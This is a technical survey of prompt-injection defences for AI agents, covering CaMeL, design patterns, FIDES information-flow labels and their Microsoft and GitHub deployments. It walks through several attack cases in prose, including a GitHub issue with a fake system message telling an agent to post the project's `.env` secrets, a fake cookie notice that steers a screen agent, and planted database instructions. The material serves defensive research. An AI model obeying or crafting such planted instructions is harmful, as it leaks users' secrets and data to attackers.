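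## March 2025: CaMeL separates the plan from untrusted data

In March 2025, Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced CaMeL ("CApabilities for MachinE Learning") in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*. In the dual-LLM pattern, an attacker can change the values a plan uses, such as an email address, without changing the plan itself. To address this, CaMeL keeps the pattern's privileged and quarantined models and also tracks where every value came from.

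### One request, step by step

In the CaMeL paper's main example, a user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting, and adds that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. Willison (2025) reproduced this example in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*.

The privileged model sees this request but not the notes. It writes a complete program before any model has read them. Simplified, the program might look like this:

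```
notes = find_file("notes from last meeting")
doc_name = query_quarantined_llm("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes, str)
address = query_quarantined_llm("What is Bob's email address?", notes, EmailStr)
document = fetch_file(doc_name)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

The language is a restricted version of Python, which the team chose because models already write Python well. They wrote an interpreter that turns the program into a tree and runs it node by node, so it can record which earlier values each new value was computed from.

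Every value has a tag that records where the data came from and who may read it. When the program computes a result from several values, the checks on that result take all of them into account. The address in this example came from the notes, so anyone who can edit the notes may have influenced it. The quarantined model has to return the type of value the program specifies, so it can return the wrong email address but not a paragraph of instructions.

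Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, which is a short Python function that checks the call's arguments and their tags. One policy might always allow the program to fetch a file. The policy for `send_email` might allow a document to go to people who already have permission to read it, and require the user's approval for anyone else.

If nobody has tampered with the notes, the quarantined model returns Bob's real address. Bob already has access to the document, so the policy allows the call without the user's approval.

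If an attacker has added a line to the notes saying that Bob has a new address, which the attacker controls, the quarantined model may well return that address. The program stays the same, because the privileged model finished writing it before anything opened the notes. When the interpreter reaches the last line, it applies the policy and checks the new address against the document's permitted readers. The address isn't among them, so the interpreter blocks the call or asks the user. With the dual-LLM pattern alone, the attacker would have received the document.

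The attacker could also change the document's name in the notes, so that the program fetches a list of salaries instead. The policy stops the program from sending the list to Bob if he isn't allowed to read it, but otherwise he gets the wrong document. CaMeL can control where data goes, but it can't ensure that the quarantined model's answers are right.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) runs the same plan with and without tags to separate the effects of the plan from those of the tags. In both versions, an attack can't add a tool call and can only make the quarantined model's answers wrong. Without tags, that is enough to leak private notes, because the quarantined model copies them into a reply and the plan sends it. Tags let a monitor check where the reply's text came from before the plan sends it.

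The privileged model can also write `if` statements and loops. Untrusted data can then decide which branch runs, but it can't add a new one. CaMeL can apply a condition's tag to what happens inside the branch, much as Fenton's design did in the 1970s. For example, in *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) describe a program that sends an email only if an account balance exceeds a threshold. CaMeL blocks the email because its arrival would reveal something about the balance. However, the same researchers found other flows that CaMeL's tracking misses.

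### Capabilities in name

The CaMeL paper calls these tags "capabilities", but they differ from object capabilities, which a program needs in order to act on anything. In CaMeL, the program can call `send_email` by name with any address. The tag on the address gives the program no power and is only a record for the policy to check. The tags are much closer to the labels in Denning's lattice model. The record of where data came from serves as an integrity label, and the list of readers serves as a confidentiality label.

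Specialists in capability security noticed this quickly. In May 2025, Karp shared the news about CaMeL on the cap-talk mailing list (Karp, 2025, *Capabilities and prompt injection*). Mark Miller replied that the tags, as Willison described them, "don't even sound vaguely like ocaps", though he called his reaction brief and cursory. "Ocaps" is his abbreviation for object capabilities, which he coined because people had already used the word "capability" so loosely that it meant very little.

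Miller thought the design sounded like taint tracking, which could be very valuable against prompt injection, but he objected to the strength of the claimed guarantee. Taint tracking works well against an honest programmer's mistakes, but malicious code can get around it. Stopping malicious code would take something like full information-flow control, which also rejects many correct programs. He suggested that one could train the model to write programs that pass such a checker.

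CaMeL partly answers this because the privileged model, rather than the attacker, writes the program, and it sees only the user's request. But Miller pointed out that a fallible programmer might occasionally write anything a malicious one would. CaMeL also assumes that the user's request is trustworthy, which it may not be, since people paste text from websites into their prompts.

### Who built it, and the first reactions

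Most of CaMeL's ten authors came from machine-learning security. Debenedetti and Tramèr had built AgentDojo, and Nicholas Carlini, Jamie Hayes and Ilia Shumailov were known for research on attacking machine-learning models and extracting data from them. Christoph Kern and Daniel Fabian came from Google's security teams. Kern had spent years working on libraries that make bugs such as SQL injection very hard to write, and Fabian had led Google's red team, which attacks the company's systems to find weaknesses.

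The paper appeared at a conference on secure and trustworthy machine learning in 2026. None of the ten people who wrote it was mainly a programming-languages theorist. The older ideas were brought to agents by people who had seen many training-based defences fail, and by engineers who had already removed one kind of injection bug by changing the tools programmers use.

Willison was enthusiastic, partly because CaMeL built on his own pattern. He wrote that it was the first defence he had seen that claimed strong guarantees, and he liked that it didn't add another model to detect attacks. He considers a detector that catches 99% of attacks inadequate, because attackers will keep looking for the other 1%. He also saw a privacy benefit, since the quarantined model's job is easier and a small model on the user's own device could do it. The company that runs the privileged model would then never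 see the user's files.

The security writer Bruce Schneier (2025) wrote in *Applying Security Engineering to Prompt Injection Security* that CaMeL "seems like an important advance", and followed this with a longer description quoted from a news article.

CaMeL itself was a research prototype. Google published the code, and the company later used part of the idea in Chrome's agent.

### What the AgentDojo results mean

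The paper's revised abstract, from June 2025, reports that CaMeL solved 77% of AgentDojo's tasks "with provable security", compared with 84% for an undefended system. The first version reported 67%, a figure that *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) still cited in July.

CaMeL's design gives good reasons to think that untrusted text can't add a tool call to the plan. But the word "provable" needs some care because, as Garby and colleagues point out, nobody had proved a theorem about the system as a whole. The CaMeL paper called formalisation a "crucial direction" for later work.

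Other published results and reruns are mostly lower:

| Result | Part of AgentDojo | Tasks solved without attacks | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL's published results with GPT-4o | All | 53.6% | 0% |
| *SecureClaw*'s adapted rerun | All | 29.9% | 0 of 629 |
| Garby and colleagues, GPT-5.2, policies off | Banking | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
| Garby and colleagues, GPT-5.2, policies on | Banking | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |

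Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025) give the GPT-4o figures in a comparison in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, but they couldn't fully reproduce them. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a rival defence, had to adapt CaMeL's code to run it on the same cases. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes CaMeL's task performance as comparable to an undefended agent's, which fits the revised abstract but not these reruns.

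The comparison by Garby and colleagues is the most informative, because only the policies change between the two rows. Turning them on cut successful runs from 32 of 48 to 18 of 48. Many banking tasks involve paying someone whose details are in a file or a message, and the policies don't let untrusted data decide where money goes. In real use, the assistant could ask its user to approve the payment, but AgentDojo has no user to ask, so a blocked payment usually counts as a failed task.

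Most attacks failed even with the policies off. In 97 of the 144 combinations of a banking task and an attack, the attacker needs a tool call that the plan would never contain. For instance, if the user only wants a summary of recent payments, the plan won't include a call to send money. Only the other 47 combinations really test the policies.

In one strange exception, a task asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a loop that matched each instruction in the file to one of the tools. This loop acted as a small agent inside the plan, so with the policies off, an attacker who controlled the file could again choose the tool calls.

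The original CaMeL evaluation also had two successful injections, which Garby and colleagues re-examined. In one, the user had asked the agent to pay whatever a document said, and the attacker had changed the document. The CaMeL paper treats this as outside the problem it addresses. In the other, the assistant quoted a hotel review word for word, and AgentDojo counted this as a successful attack because the text matched.

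Blocking every attack in AgentDojo isn't strong evidence of security on its own. Bhagwatkar and colleagues tested a simple "sanitizer", a model that removes suspicious instructions from each tool's output. With GPT-4o, it also reduced successful attacks to zero, and the agent still solved 74% of the tasks. The researchers concluded that the benchmark's attacks were too weak, although these numbers alone make the sanitizer look clearly better than CaMeL.

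*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) then had a model rewrite the attacks repeatedly, keeping the versions that worked. One filter had blocked every standard attack on an agent that used GPT-4o-mini, but 28% of the rewritten attacks got through. Some defences still gave protection, especially those that limit what the agent can do. The main argument for a design like CaMeL is that a filter has to recognise each new wording, while CaMeL's plan stays the same whatever the email says.

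### Costs, failures and admitted limits

In the CaMeL paper's tests, the median AgentDojo task used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens with the defence as without it. Tokens are the pieces of text that models process and providers charge for. Developers also have to describe the format of every tool's output in advance, because CaMeL's privileged model has to write code to handle results it will never see. An ordinary agent can work out the format by looking at the result.

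The same problem caused most of the task failures in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, a later study by Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026). Sometimes the need for another step becomes clear only after a tool call returns its result. An ordinary agent can add the step, but CaMeL can only follow paths already in the program. In other cases, a tool had no data for the requested dates and returned data for different ones, and the program used that data without detecting the mismatch.

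CaMeL therefore works best for requests like "email this report to Anna", where the user says what should happen. It struggles more with "deal with whatever is in this email", because the actions needed depend on what the email says. Ma and colleagues found that attacks on the agents they tested succeeded most often on this kind of request, and that much ordinary use of agents is similarly vague. If people mainly want assistants for such tasks, CaMeL's strictness will be a serious drawback.

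The CaMeL paper acknowledges that it doesn't fully solve prompt injection. Someone has to write and maintain the policies, and every exception sent to the user adds an approval request, which the paper warns causes fatigue. Willison was also worried about the burden on users. After two decades of working on application security, he still found Amazon's permission settings confusing, so he doubted that ordinary users would do well with CaMeL's policies.

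Tallam and Miller, who work at a security company, expected a similar problem in organisations with hundreds of tools, where separate policy functions would become inconsistent and hard to audit. They suggested letting low-risk actions through after a basic check and saving the strictest approvals for actions like bank transfers. Their paper proposes these changes to CaMeL but doesn't test them.

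The CaMeL paper also acknowledges that information can leak through side channels, which are signals other than the data a program deliberately sends. If a program fetches a web page once for every unit of a secret number, the website's owner can learn the number by counting the visits. An error that occurs only for certain values can also reveal information, as can the time a program takes to run.

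Another weakness CaMeL shares with the dual-LLM pattern is that the assistant may still show an attacker's text to the user. Tallam and Miller give the example of a PDF with a hidden line about forwarding the file to an outside address. If the assistant's summary includes that line, the user might forward the file.

### Simpler designs for narrower agents

Few developers will want to write an interpreter, as CaMeL requires. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (June 2025) offered six designs, most of them simpler than CaMeL, in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*. The group included Debenedetti, Tramèr and Fabian from the CaMeL team, two founders of Invariant Labs, and Andrew Paverd of Microsoft, who also worked on FIDES. Others came from IBM, Swisscom and EPFL, a Swiss university.

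They thought general-purpose agents were unlikely to give reliable guarantees with the current kind of language model, so they looked for more limited agents that would still be useful. Their rule is that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must have no way to trigger an action with harmful consequences. The six patterns apply this rule with varying strictness.

An action selector lets the model choose from a fixed list of actions but never shows it the results. A customer-service bot might send a customer a link to their last order or point them to the password page. Data from the tools can't inject instructions because the model never reads it, but for the same reason the bot can't answer a question about the order.

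Plan-then-execute lets the agent use results, but only after it has fixed its list of tool calls. If the user asks it to send today's schedule to their boss, it plans to read the calendar and then email the boss. A malicious calendar entry can't add another call or change the recipient, but it can still change the body of the email.

In the map-reduce pattern, a separate model without tools reads each document and returns a limited answer, such as yes or no. Suppose an agent has to find this month's invoices and send them to the accounts department. A malicious file can cause the model to mark it as an invoice, but it can't affect how the model reads the other files or make the agent send something else.

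The catalogue also includes Willison's dual-LLM pattern and code-then-execute, a more general version of CaMeL that fixes the program in advance but doesn't require CaMeL's tags. Without the tags, a calendar entry can still change what the email to the boss says, as it can under plan-then-execute.

Context minimisation deals with attacks in the user's own prompt. A customer might ask a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and include text meant to get a large discount. The system turns the request into a database query, then deletes the customer's prompt, so the model writes its answer from the retrieved price without the manipulative text.

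The paper describes example applications ranging from a file assistant to a medical chatbot, but doesn't measure how well the patterns work. The hardest case is probably a software engineering agent, which is useful partly because it can read other people's code and documentation. The safest suggestion is to have a quarantined model convert the documentation into a strict list of functions, with names of, for example, at most 30 characters, but the agent then loses all the explanations and examples.

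Willison (2025) praised the paper's realism but wondered whether even a 30-character limit was safe. An attacker could perhaps name a function `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`, referring to a command that deletes files. Limiting the format makes an attack harder to write, but a language model can still read meaning into a name.

### Extending CaMeL to screens and teams of agents

AgentDojo's tools, such as `send_email`, have clear names and purposes. Many newer agents instead operate a computer by viewing the screen and clicking, and they usually take a new screenshot after each action. CaMeL's privileged model can't view these screenshots, because they may contain text from an attacker.

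Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) got around this in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* by having the privileged model plan for many possible screens in advance. The program uses a quarantined vision model to identify what is on the screen, checks a condition such as whether there is a cookie banner, and takes the branch for that case. The team included Tramèr and Shumailov, who had moved to a startup called AI Sequrity Company.

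These programs averaged 213 lines and 41 tool calls, compared with 52 lines and five tool calls for AgentDojo, and about half of each plan never ran. The extra branches helped, though. On 60 tasks from OSWorld, a benchmark that uses real desktop programs, CaMeL solved 11 within three attempts with a generic prompt and 35 with instructions to observe, check and then act.

According to the paper's abstract, this design keeps up to 57% of frontier models' performance. That figure is generous because it counts a task as solved if any of five attempts succeeded. Of the 109 automatically graded tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 solved without the defence, the CaMeL version solved 62 by that measure, but only 31, or 28%, with a single attempt. A user would need some way to tell which attempt had worked, and might not want an agent to try a purchase five times.

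Token use was more reasonable, at 1.88 times that of the undefended agent. Applying the same planning method to FIDES, which calls its planner again after every step, took 29.6 times as many tokens.

An attacker can still influence which branch the program takes, which the researchers call branch steering. The researchers put a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement. The plan already contained a step for dismissing cookie notices, so the agent clicked on the advertisement and went to the attacker's website. The researchers tried comparing the screenshot with the page's underlying code and asking a second model, but neither check was reliable. CaMeL's policies are little help here. A policy can restrict who receives an email, but a click on the screen could have very different effects, such as logging the user in or deleting a file.

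Peters-Gill and colleagues found a different gap that arises when several agents work together. They gave CaMeL to three agents: one that read a database, one that sent messages, and an orchestrator that divided up the work. The user asked for a summary of some job applications to be sent to Julie on Slack. An attacker had put an instruction in the database to email the applicants' details to an outside address.

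The database agent and the orchestrator both kept to their plans, but the orchestrator pasted the summary into its request to the messaging agent. The messaging agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so its privileged model read the attacker's instruction and added the email to its plan. Each agent followed CaMeL's rules, but untrusted text was treated as trusted once one agent passed it to another.

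Their fix, multi-CaMeL, splits each request into an instruction and a set of variables. The receiving agent's privileged model gets only the instruction, and the interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. Tags stay attached to the variables as they pass between agents.

They tested this with five models on a version of AgentDojo divided among several agents, with 949 attack cases for each model. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent used CaMeL separately, and none with multi-CaMeL. Most of the successful attacks without CaMeL were against two older models, GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without CaMeL, so the test can't show whether CaMeL made it safer. The researchers warn that stronger attacks have succeeded against every frontier model tested in a large public competition.

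Better models also lost less performance. On a separate benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, using CaMeL in each agent lowered the success rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 points for GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Multi-CaMeL lowered the rate for those two by less than one further point. All of these runs had CaMeL's policies switched off, so the figures don't include the effect of the policies, which halved its success rate on AgentDojo's banking tasks.

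## Information-flow labels: from Microsoft's FIDES paper to shipped code

CaMeL fixes its plan before any model has read untrusted data, so it struggles when the next step depends on what a tool returns. In May 2025, two months after CaMeL, nine Microsoft researchers published a design called FIDES in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*. FIDES keeps the ordinary agent loop, in which the model chooses one step at a time. It labels everything that passes through the loop and checks the labels before each tool call.

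Several of the nine had worked on related problems. Köpf and Zanella-Béguelin had worked on the 2023 noninterference paper, Manuel Costa had worked on detecting internet worms by tracking network data through a running program, and Shruti Tople and Ahmed Salem had studied privacy in machine learning. Mark Russinovich, the chief technology officer of Microsoft's Azure cloud business, was best known for his expertise in Windows internals. His presence on the team probably helped get the design into products.

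### Labels in an ordinary agent loop

Costa and colleagues divide the harness into a planner and a loop. After each message, the planner chooses whether to query the model, call a tool, or finish and answer the user. The loop carries out that action and passes the result back, so it can serve as the reference monitor.

FIDES labels data for integrity and confidentiality in the usual way, except that a confidentiality label can also be a list of the people who may read the data. When the agent combines two documents, only people who may read both may read the result. If Ann, Ben and Cara may read one report, and Ben, Cara and Dev may read another, a summary of both has the label

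{Ann, Ben, Cara} ∩ {Ben, Cara, Dev} = {Ben, Cara}.

This is still Denning's join, because a shorter list of readers is a more restrictive label.

The conversation has a context label, the join of the labels on all its messages. To be safe, FIDES gives this label to everything the model writes. When a tool runs, its result gets the join of the labels on the call, its arguments and any stored data the tool may have read.

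The loop can then enforce two basic policies. An integrity policy allows a consequential action, such as paying a bill, only if the call and its arguments are Trusted. A confidentiality policy allows the agent to send information only to people permitted to read it. The confidentiality policy doesn't prevent prompt injection on its own, since a stranger's email could still make the agent send messages to people permitted to read them.

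A developer can require both policies or accept a call that satisfies either one. The second option lets a user have the agent send a document to someone new, provided no untrusted text has influenced the call. Steve Zdancewic and Andrew Myers named this idea robust declassification in 2001. *Flowsh* (2026), a design for a command shell that tracks information flow for agents, presents the same two policies.

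### Hiding text and asking narrow questions

If an agent with these policies reads one email from a stranger, its context becomes Untrusted and it can no longer do much. To avoid this, the FIDES planner hides tool results whose labels are more restrictive than the context's. It stores each result in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name.

FIDES hides data field by field. In a list of emails, the model might see the dates and the senders' addresses, with `#read_emails_0.subject` in place of a subject line. Unlike Willison's dual-LLM pattern, FIDES hides only what would change the context label, so its planner usually receives more information.

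Suppose the user asks the agent to send the top three emails to a colleague on Slack. The model calls the tool that reads mail, gets back a variable, and passes it to the tool that sends messages. The model makes this second call without reading any of the emails, so the call is Trusted even though the message is Untrusted. A policy can require a Trusted call and a Trusted recipient while allowing an Untrusted message. If the user wants a summary instead, a quarantined model writes it, as in Willison's pattern.

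Some tasks are harder because the planner has to learn something from the data. When a user asks the agent to check their emails for a meeting request and create a calendar event if there is one, no single list of tool calls is right for every inbox. Costa and colleagues call such a task data dependent.

For these tasks, FIDES can restrict the quarantined model to certain answers, such as true or false, and enforce the restriction during generation, as LMQL does. The planner then reads the answer. If it is true, the planner requests the date, time and participants from the quarantined model and passes them to the calendar tool without reading them. An attacker can make the answer wrong or change the meeting time, but can't fit a new instruction into a true-or-false answer.

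FIDES records the restriction in the label, which becomes a pair (ℓ, μ). The security label ℓ works as before, and μ is the type of the data. The types form an order according to how much information they can carry:

true/false ⊑ a fixed list of choices ⊑ free text.

A policy can then accept an Untrusted true or false where it would refuse Untrusted text. This is a form of endorsement, and Garby and colleagues later criticised FIDES's relaxations of this kind. Controlling that one bit is sometimes enough for an attacker. For example, if the user says to pay an invoice once the supplier has confirmed delivery, an attacker who changes the answer from false to true can get the money sent.

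### What the guarantee covers

The guarantee that Costa and colleagues offer is called explicit secrecy, and it is weaker than noninterference. Let d₁ and d₂ be two versions of the stored data that contain the same public information, written d₁ ~ d₂. Suppose the agent runs on d₁ and makes some tool calls, and let g be the combined effect of those calls on the data. Explicit secrecy requires that, for every such d₂,

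g(d₁) ~ g(d₂).

Explicit secrecy requires the public part to come out the same when the same calls are replayed on data d₂, which has different secrets. Noninterference requires this even when the agent runs again from the beginning on d₂, where it might choose different calls. Explicit secrecy therefore rules out copying a secret into a public place, but not revealing information through the choice of calls, which is a case of Denning's implicit flows.

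The team deliberately chose the weaker property because, they say, noninterference would essentially stop the agent from writing anything public after it had read anything secret. Web browsers and TaintDroid, a system that tracks private data on Android phones, were already built on the same compromise. Costa and colleagues also object that the practical version of f-secure allows some of these implicit flows, despite the system's noninterference proof.

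The FIDES paper defines explicit secrecy formally and argues that the labelled loop can enforce it, but doesn't state this as a separate theorem. The argument treats the model as deterministic, although language models usually choose their words partly at random, and it leaves out side channels such as timing. It also assumes that the labels are correct and that the user's messages, the developer's instructions and the tool descriptions are trustworthy. The guarantee therefore doesn't cover a malicious MCP service that puts instructions in a tool's description.

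### Results on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, using one of the benchmark's stronger attacks. By their count, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent, 21 against FIDES with its policies off, and none with the policies on. AgentDojo's own scoring recorded three successful attacks against the full system, but the team checked these by hand and rejected them. In some of the rejected cases, AgentDojo had counted an attempt to invite an outsider to Slack, although the policy had blocked the call.

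The policies also stopped every attack on an ordinary agent that had labels but no hidden variables. The variables let the agent finish more tasks without breaking a policy. The table below shows the percentage of tasks completed without attacks when the agents used o1, an OpenAI reasoning model.

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
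| Ordinary agent with labels and policies | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 |
| FIDES with policies | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |

The team's main result is that FIDES completes 16% more tasks than a basic planner when both have the policies on. Averaged over the four settings, FIDES completes about 61% of tasks and the unprotected agent about 84%. The paper also reports a much smaller loss of 6.3%, but this applies only with the policies off.

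The perfect security score is less impressive than it looks because of how the team chose the labels. AgentDojo doesn't supply any, so the team marked a field as Untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. The labels therefore covered every place an attack could appear in the tests. A company labelling its own data wouldn't have a list of those places in advance. The team also left out the restricted answers described above, which it found unnecessary for most of AgentDojo's tasks.

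Many of the failures were intended. Several banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which an integrity policy is supposed to prevent. GPT-4o also mixed up variable names and sometimes made unnecessary calls that could make the context Untrusted.

Some of the successes were partly luck. One task asks the agent to change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. GPT-4o judged a large payment suspicious by its amount, without opening the Untrusted description, so the context stayed Trusted and the policy allowed the change. Another task asks for the price of a New Year's gift. An agent that couldn't read any descriptions guessed that the gift was the only payment made on 1 January, and it was right.

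### The experimental release and the hostile issue

By the summer of 2026, Microsoft and its subsidiary GitHub had put labels into four pieces of software, with different levels of commitment.

| Software | What it does with labels | Status |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Agent Framework | Tracks them and checks tool calls | Experimental, opt-in |
| GitHub MCP server | Attaches them to results | Optional |
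| GitHub Copilot CLI | Tracks them and checks some GitHub tools | Experimental, behind a flag |
| GitHub Agentic Workflows | Removes low-integrity content before the agent sees it | On by default for public repositories |

Microsoft released FIDES in Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents, on 20 May 2026. The announcement, *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), works through the example of an agent that sorts a software project's bug reports, which GitHub calls issues. The agent can read issues, read and write files, and post public comments.

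An attacker opens an issue about a build that fails on macOS. Below a realistic error message, the attacker adds a fake system message. In it, the attacker claims that the user has authorised access to the project's secrets, and tells the agent to read the `.env` file, post its contents as a comment and not mention the instruction. Suppose the model treats all of this as genuine.

| Tool call | Label on the result | Context label afterwards | Decision |
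|---|---|---|---|
| Read the issue | Untrusted, Public | Untrusted, Public | Allowed |
| Read `.env` | Trusted, Private | Untrusted, Private | Allowed |
| Post a comment | None | Untrusted, Private | Blocked |

The framework blocks the comment because the developer has declared that comments can contain only Public information. If the issue had instead contained an instruction to overwrite a file, the framework would have blocked the write too, because the file-writing tool isn't allowed to run in an Untrusted context. Neither block depends on the model detecting the attack.

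Microsoft turned off automatic hiding for this example to show that the checks work even when the model reads the attacker's text. With the default settings, the issue would go into a variable and only a quarantined model would read it.

A developer can have the framework ask the user to approve a blocked call instead of refusing it. One careless approval can then publish the secrets. Microsoft lists these approvals among the current limitations because the prompt shows the user only part of the reasoning behind the block.

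The most worrying limitation is that unlabelled tools count as Trusted and Public. If a developer forgets to label the tool that reads issues, the attacker's text enters the conversation as if the developer had written it. This default is the opposite of Saltzer and Schroeder's fail-safe defaults, and a missing label causes no error. Microsoft asked developers whether unlabelled tools should count as Untrusted instead, which would be safer but block more at first.

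Microsoft also warns that once an Untrusted issue enters the context, the rest of the run stays Untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes the issue. The quarantined model doesn't support multi-turn conversation, so the agent has to get what it needs through single questions.

### Labels in GitHub's tools

Labels are more useful if the services that supply data attach them, because the data's origin is known there. GitHub's MCP server, which gives agents access to code and issues, can now attach labels. The code documented in pkg.go.dev's *ifc* (2026), published on 18 May, only defines the labels, and a separate service enforces them. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, which describes the prototypes and was online by June 2026, explains how the parts fit together.

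A developer turns the labels on by adding a line to the server's configuration. The server then labels everything from a public repository as public and untrusted, and everything from a private repository as private and trusted. These crude labels are enough to stop an attack that researchers had demonstrated about a year earlier. In that attack, someone opens an issue in a public repository requesting information from a private one, and an agent with access to both posts the information in a public comment. With the labels on, the agent's context is labeled untrusted and private by the time the agent tries to post, so a policy blocks the comment. An agent that works only with public repositories, or only with private ones, is not interrupted.

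Copilot CLI, GitHub's coding agent for the command line, can enforce such policies if the user starts it with the setting `FIDES_IFC=true`. It keeps a context label and checks calls to selected tools on the GitHub MCP server. The feature didn't cover that server's other tools or any other MCP servers when Microsoft described it. Neither company appears to have changed the status of these experiments between June and December 2026.

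Microsoft also gives an example with no attacker. Alex asks an agent to answer the unanswered email in his inbox. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales figures. Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet, has written to ask about them. Each email may be read by the people who sent and received it, so after the agent has read both, anything it writes has the label

{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.

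Marco isn't on the list, so the agent can't send him the reply without asking Alex. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the list would have been {Alex, Marco} and the agent could have sent the reply without asking. A filter that looks for malicious instructions would miss this leak, because neither email contains any.

The example also shows how much these labels can block. If Marco had asked only whether Alex was free for lunch, the reply would have had the same label, and the agent would still have had to ask.

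Extending this to other services takes work. Microsoft published a gateway that adds labels to the results of ordinary MCP servers, but someone has to describe each tool's output format, write a function that passes labels from the tool's arguments to its results, and write or choose a policy. Microsoft suggests that the short annotations many tools already have could replace some of this work. For example, a tool annotated as destructive could always require approval. The company plans to propose adding labels and policies to MCP itself, which would help if many services adopted them.

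GitHub uses labels differently in Agentic Workflows, which lets a project run agents automatically for jobs such as sorting issues or reviewing code. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* describes a system that ranks content by who wrote it and whether a maintainer has approved it. Code that a maintainer has merged ranks highest, followed by content from the project's owners, members and collaborators. Content from other contributors ranks lower, and content from people with no history in the project ranks lower still.

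Each workflow has a minimum level. When the agent requests a list of issues, a gateway removes those below the minimum before they reach the model. According to GitHub, public repositories automatically use "approved" as the minimum unless the developer sets another, while private repositories have no filter by default. Because of the default for public repositories, this is the only one of the four uses of labels that protects people who don't know about information-flow control.

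The filter would otherwise make it impossible to triage bug reports from strangers, so maintainers can raise an item's level by adding a chosen tag to an issue or, if the project enables the feature, by giving the item a thumbs-up. In Denning's tradition, this is endorsement. A maintainer who gives a comment a thumbs-up without noticing a hidden instruction endorses the instruction too.

The filter is based on decentralised information-flow control, which Andrew Myers and Barbara Liskov introduced in 1997. The component that enforces the rules has no GitHub-specific logic and compares labels only by checking whether one set of tags contains another. Separate pieces of code, called guards, assign tags to each kind of data. GitHub can therefore add a service such as Jira by writing a new guard, without changing the enforcement component.

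So far, the system enforces only half of the theory. It tracks which data came from private repositories but doesn't stop the agent from leaking it, and GitHub Next acknowledges that the filter can't prevent leaks between repositories. Aident's *How to Secure GitHub Agentic Workflows Against Prompt Injection* reports an attack that shows the risk. In GitLost, which Noma Security disclosed on 6 July 2026, a public issue steered a workflow that could read private repositories and post public comments. A separate container for the agent and a firewall between it and the internet, both described in GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026), limit the damage from such attacks.

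### Label creep and the replies to it

All these systems suffer from label creep, so a long task can end with the agent unable to do anything useful. Hiding data in variables delays this, but many tasks eventually require the planner to read some of that data.

One response is to divide the work among several agents, so that a restrictive label on one doesn't affect the others. Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) measured how much this approach could achieve in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*. They work at the University of Wisconsin–Madison, where Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao had built f-secure. Their coauthor Patrick McDaniel had helped create TaintDroid.

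Their study ran no language model. They simulated tasks as random networks of tool calls, in which some calls needed the results of others, and distributed the calls among five to twenty agents. A few calls were marked as sensitive. An agent became sensitive when it made one of these calls or received data from a sensitive agent, and it stayed that way. The researchers measured the cost as

loss = (tool calls that are sensitive or run on a sensitive agent) / (all tool calls).

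They compared different ways to connect the agents, such as a ring, or a star in which everything goes through a central agent. With five agents and four sensitive calls out of twenty, loss was about five percentage points higher in the star and about three points higher in the ring than in an ideal network with exactly the connections the task needed. Denser networks did better because data could go straight to the agent that needed it, without affecting others on the way. Across nine networks, density and loss had a correlation of −0.96.

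Using more agents also reduced the loss, but in the densest networks the number of connections to monitor grew with the square of the number of agents. Giving all the sensitive tools to a few agents helped in every case. Even the ideal network had substantial losses, and Gregory and colleagues conclude that developers will also need safe ways to relax labels.

The loss figure probably overstates the loss in practice, because it counts every call a sensitive agent makes, including calls that a policy would allow. Real agents might also order their calls more sensibly than a random simulation does.

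*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) presents Prudentia, a later design from the FIDES group. Prudentia shows the model the labels and policies so that it can look for a plan that complies with the policies. If none exists, the model can either endorse a piece of untrusted data or ask the user to approve an action.

In *APPA*, Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026) focus on what should happen after a call is blocked. Their corresponding author works at Archestra, a company in this field. They prove that if a call is blocked because the context is too restrictive, reading more data can never unblock it, since each new label can only restrict the context further. APPA therefore responds to a blocked call with a list of steps that could fix it, such as asking for approval of that exact call or running the data through a trusted program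 that removes the sensitive parts.

Another remedy is to avoid the restrictive label. Suppose a support agent needs to read a public web page about a fault and then update an internal database. APPA lets it create a temporary copy of itself, called a child branch, to read the page. The agent first specifies that the child may return only a ticket number, a severity and a component name, with the last two chosen from fixed lists. Reading the page makes the child untrusted, and the child disappears after returning the three values. If the deployment's rules accept values of this form as trusted, the original agent can still write to the database. The web page can make the child return the wrong severity, so someone has to decide whether that risk is acceptable.

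APPA also addresses two weaknesses of simpler systems. A single tool might read a confidential ledger and email it to someone outside the company. A check based on the context before the call would allow this, because the agent hasn't read the ledger yet. APPA instead checks the call against the label that will apply after it. APPA also treats unlabelled data as unknown rather than as trusted and public. The agent can hold unknown data, but a sensitive tool won't accept it until a trusted program has labelled it.

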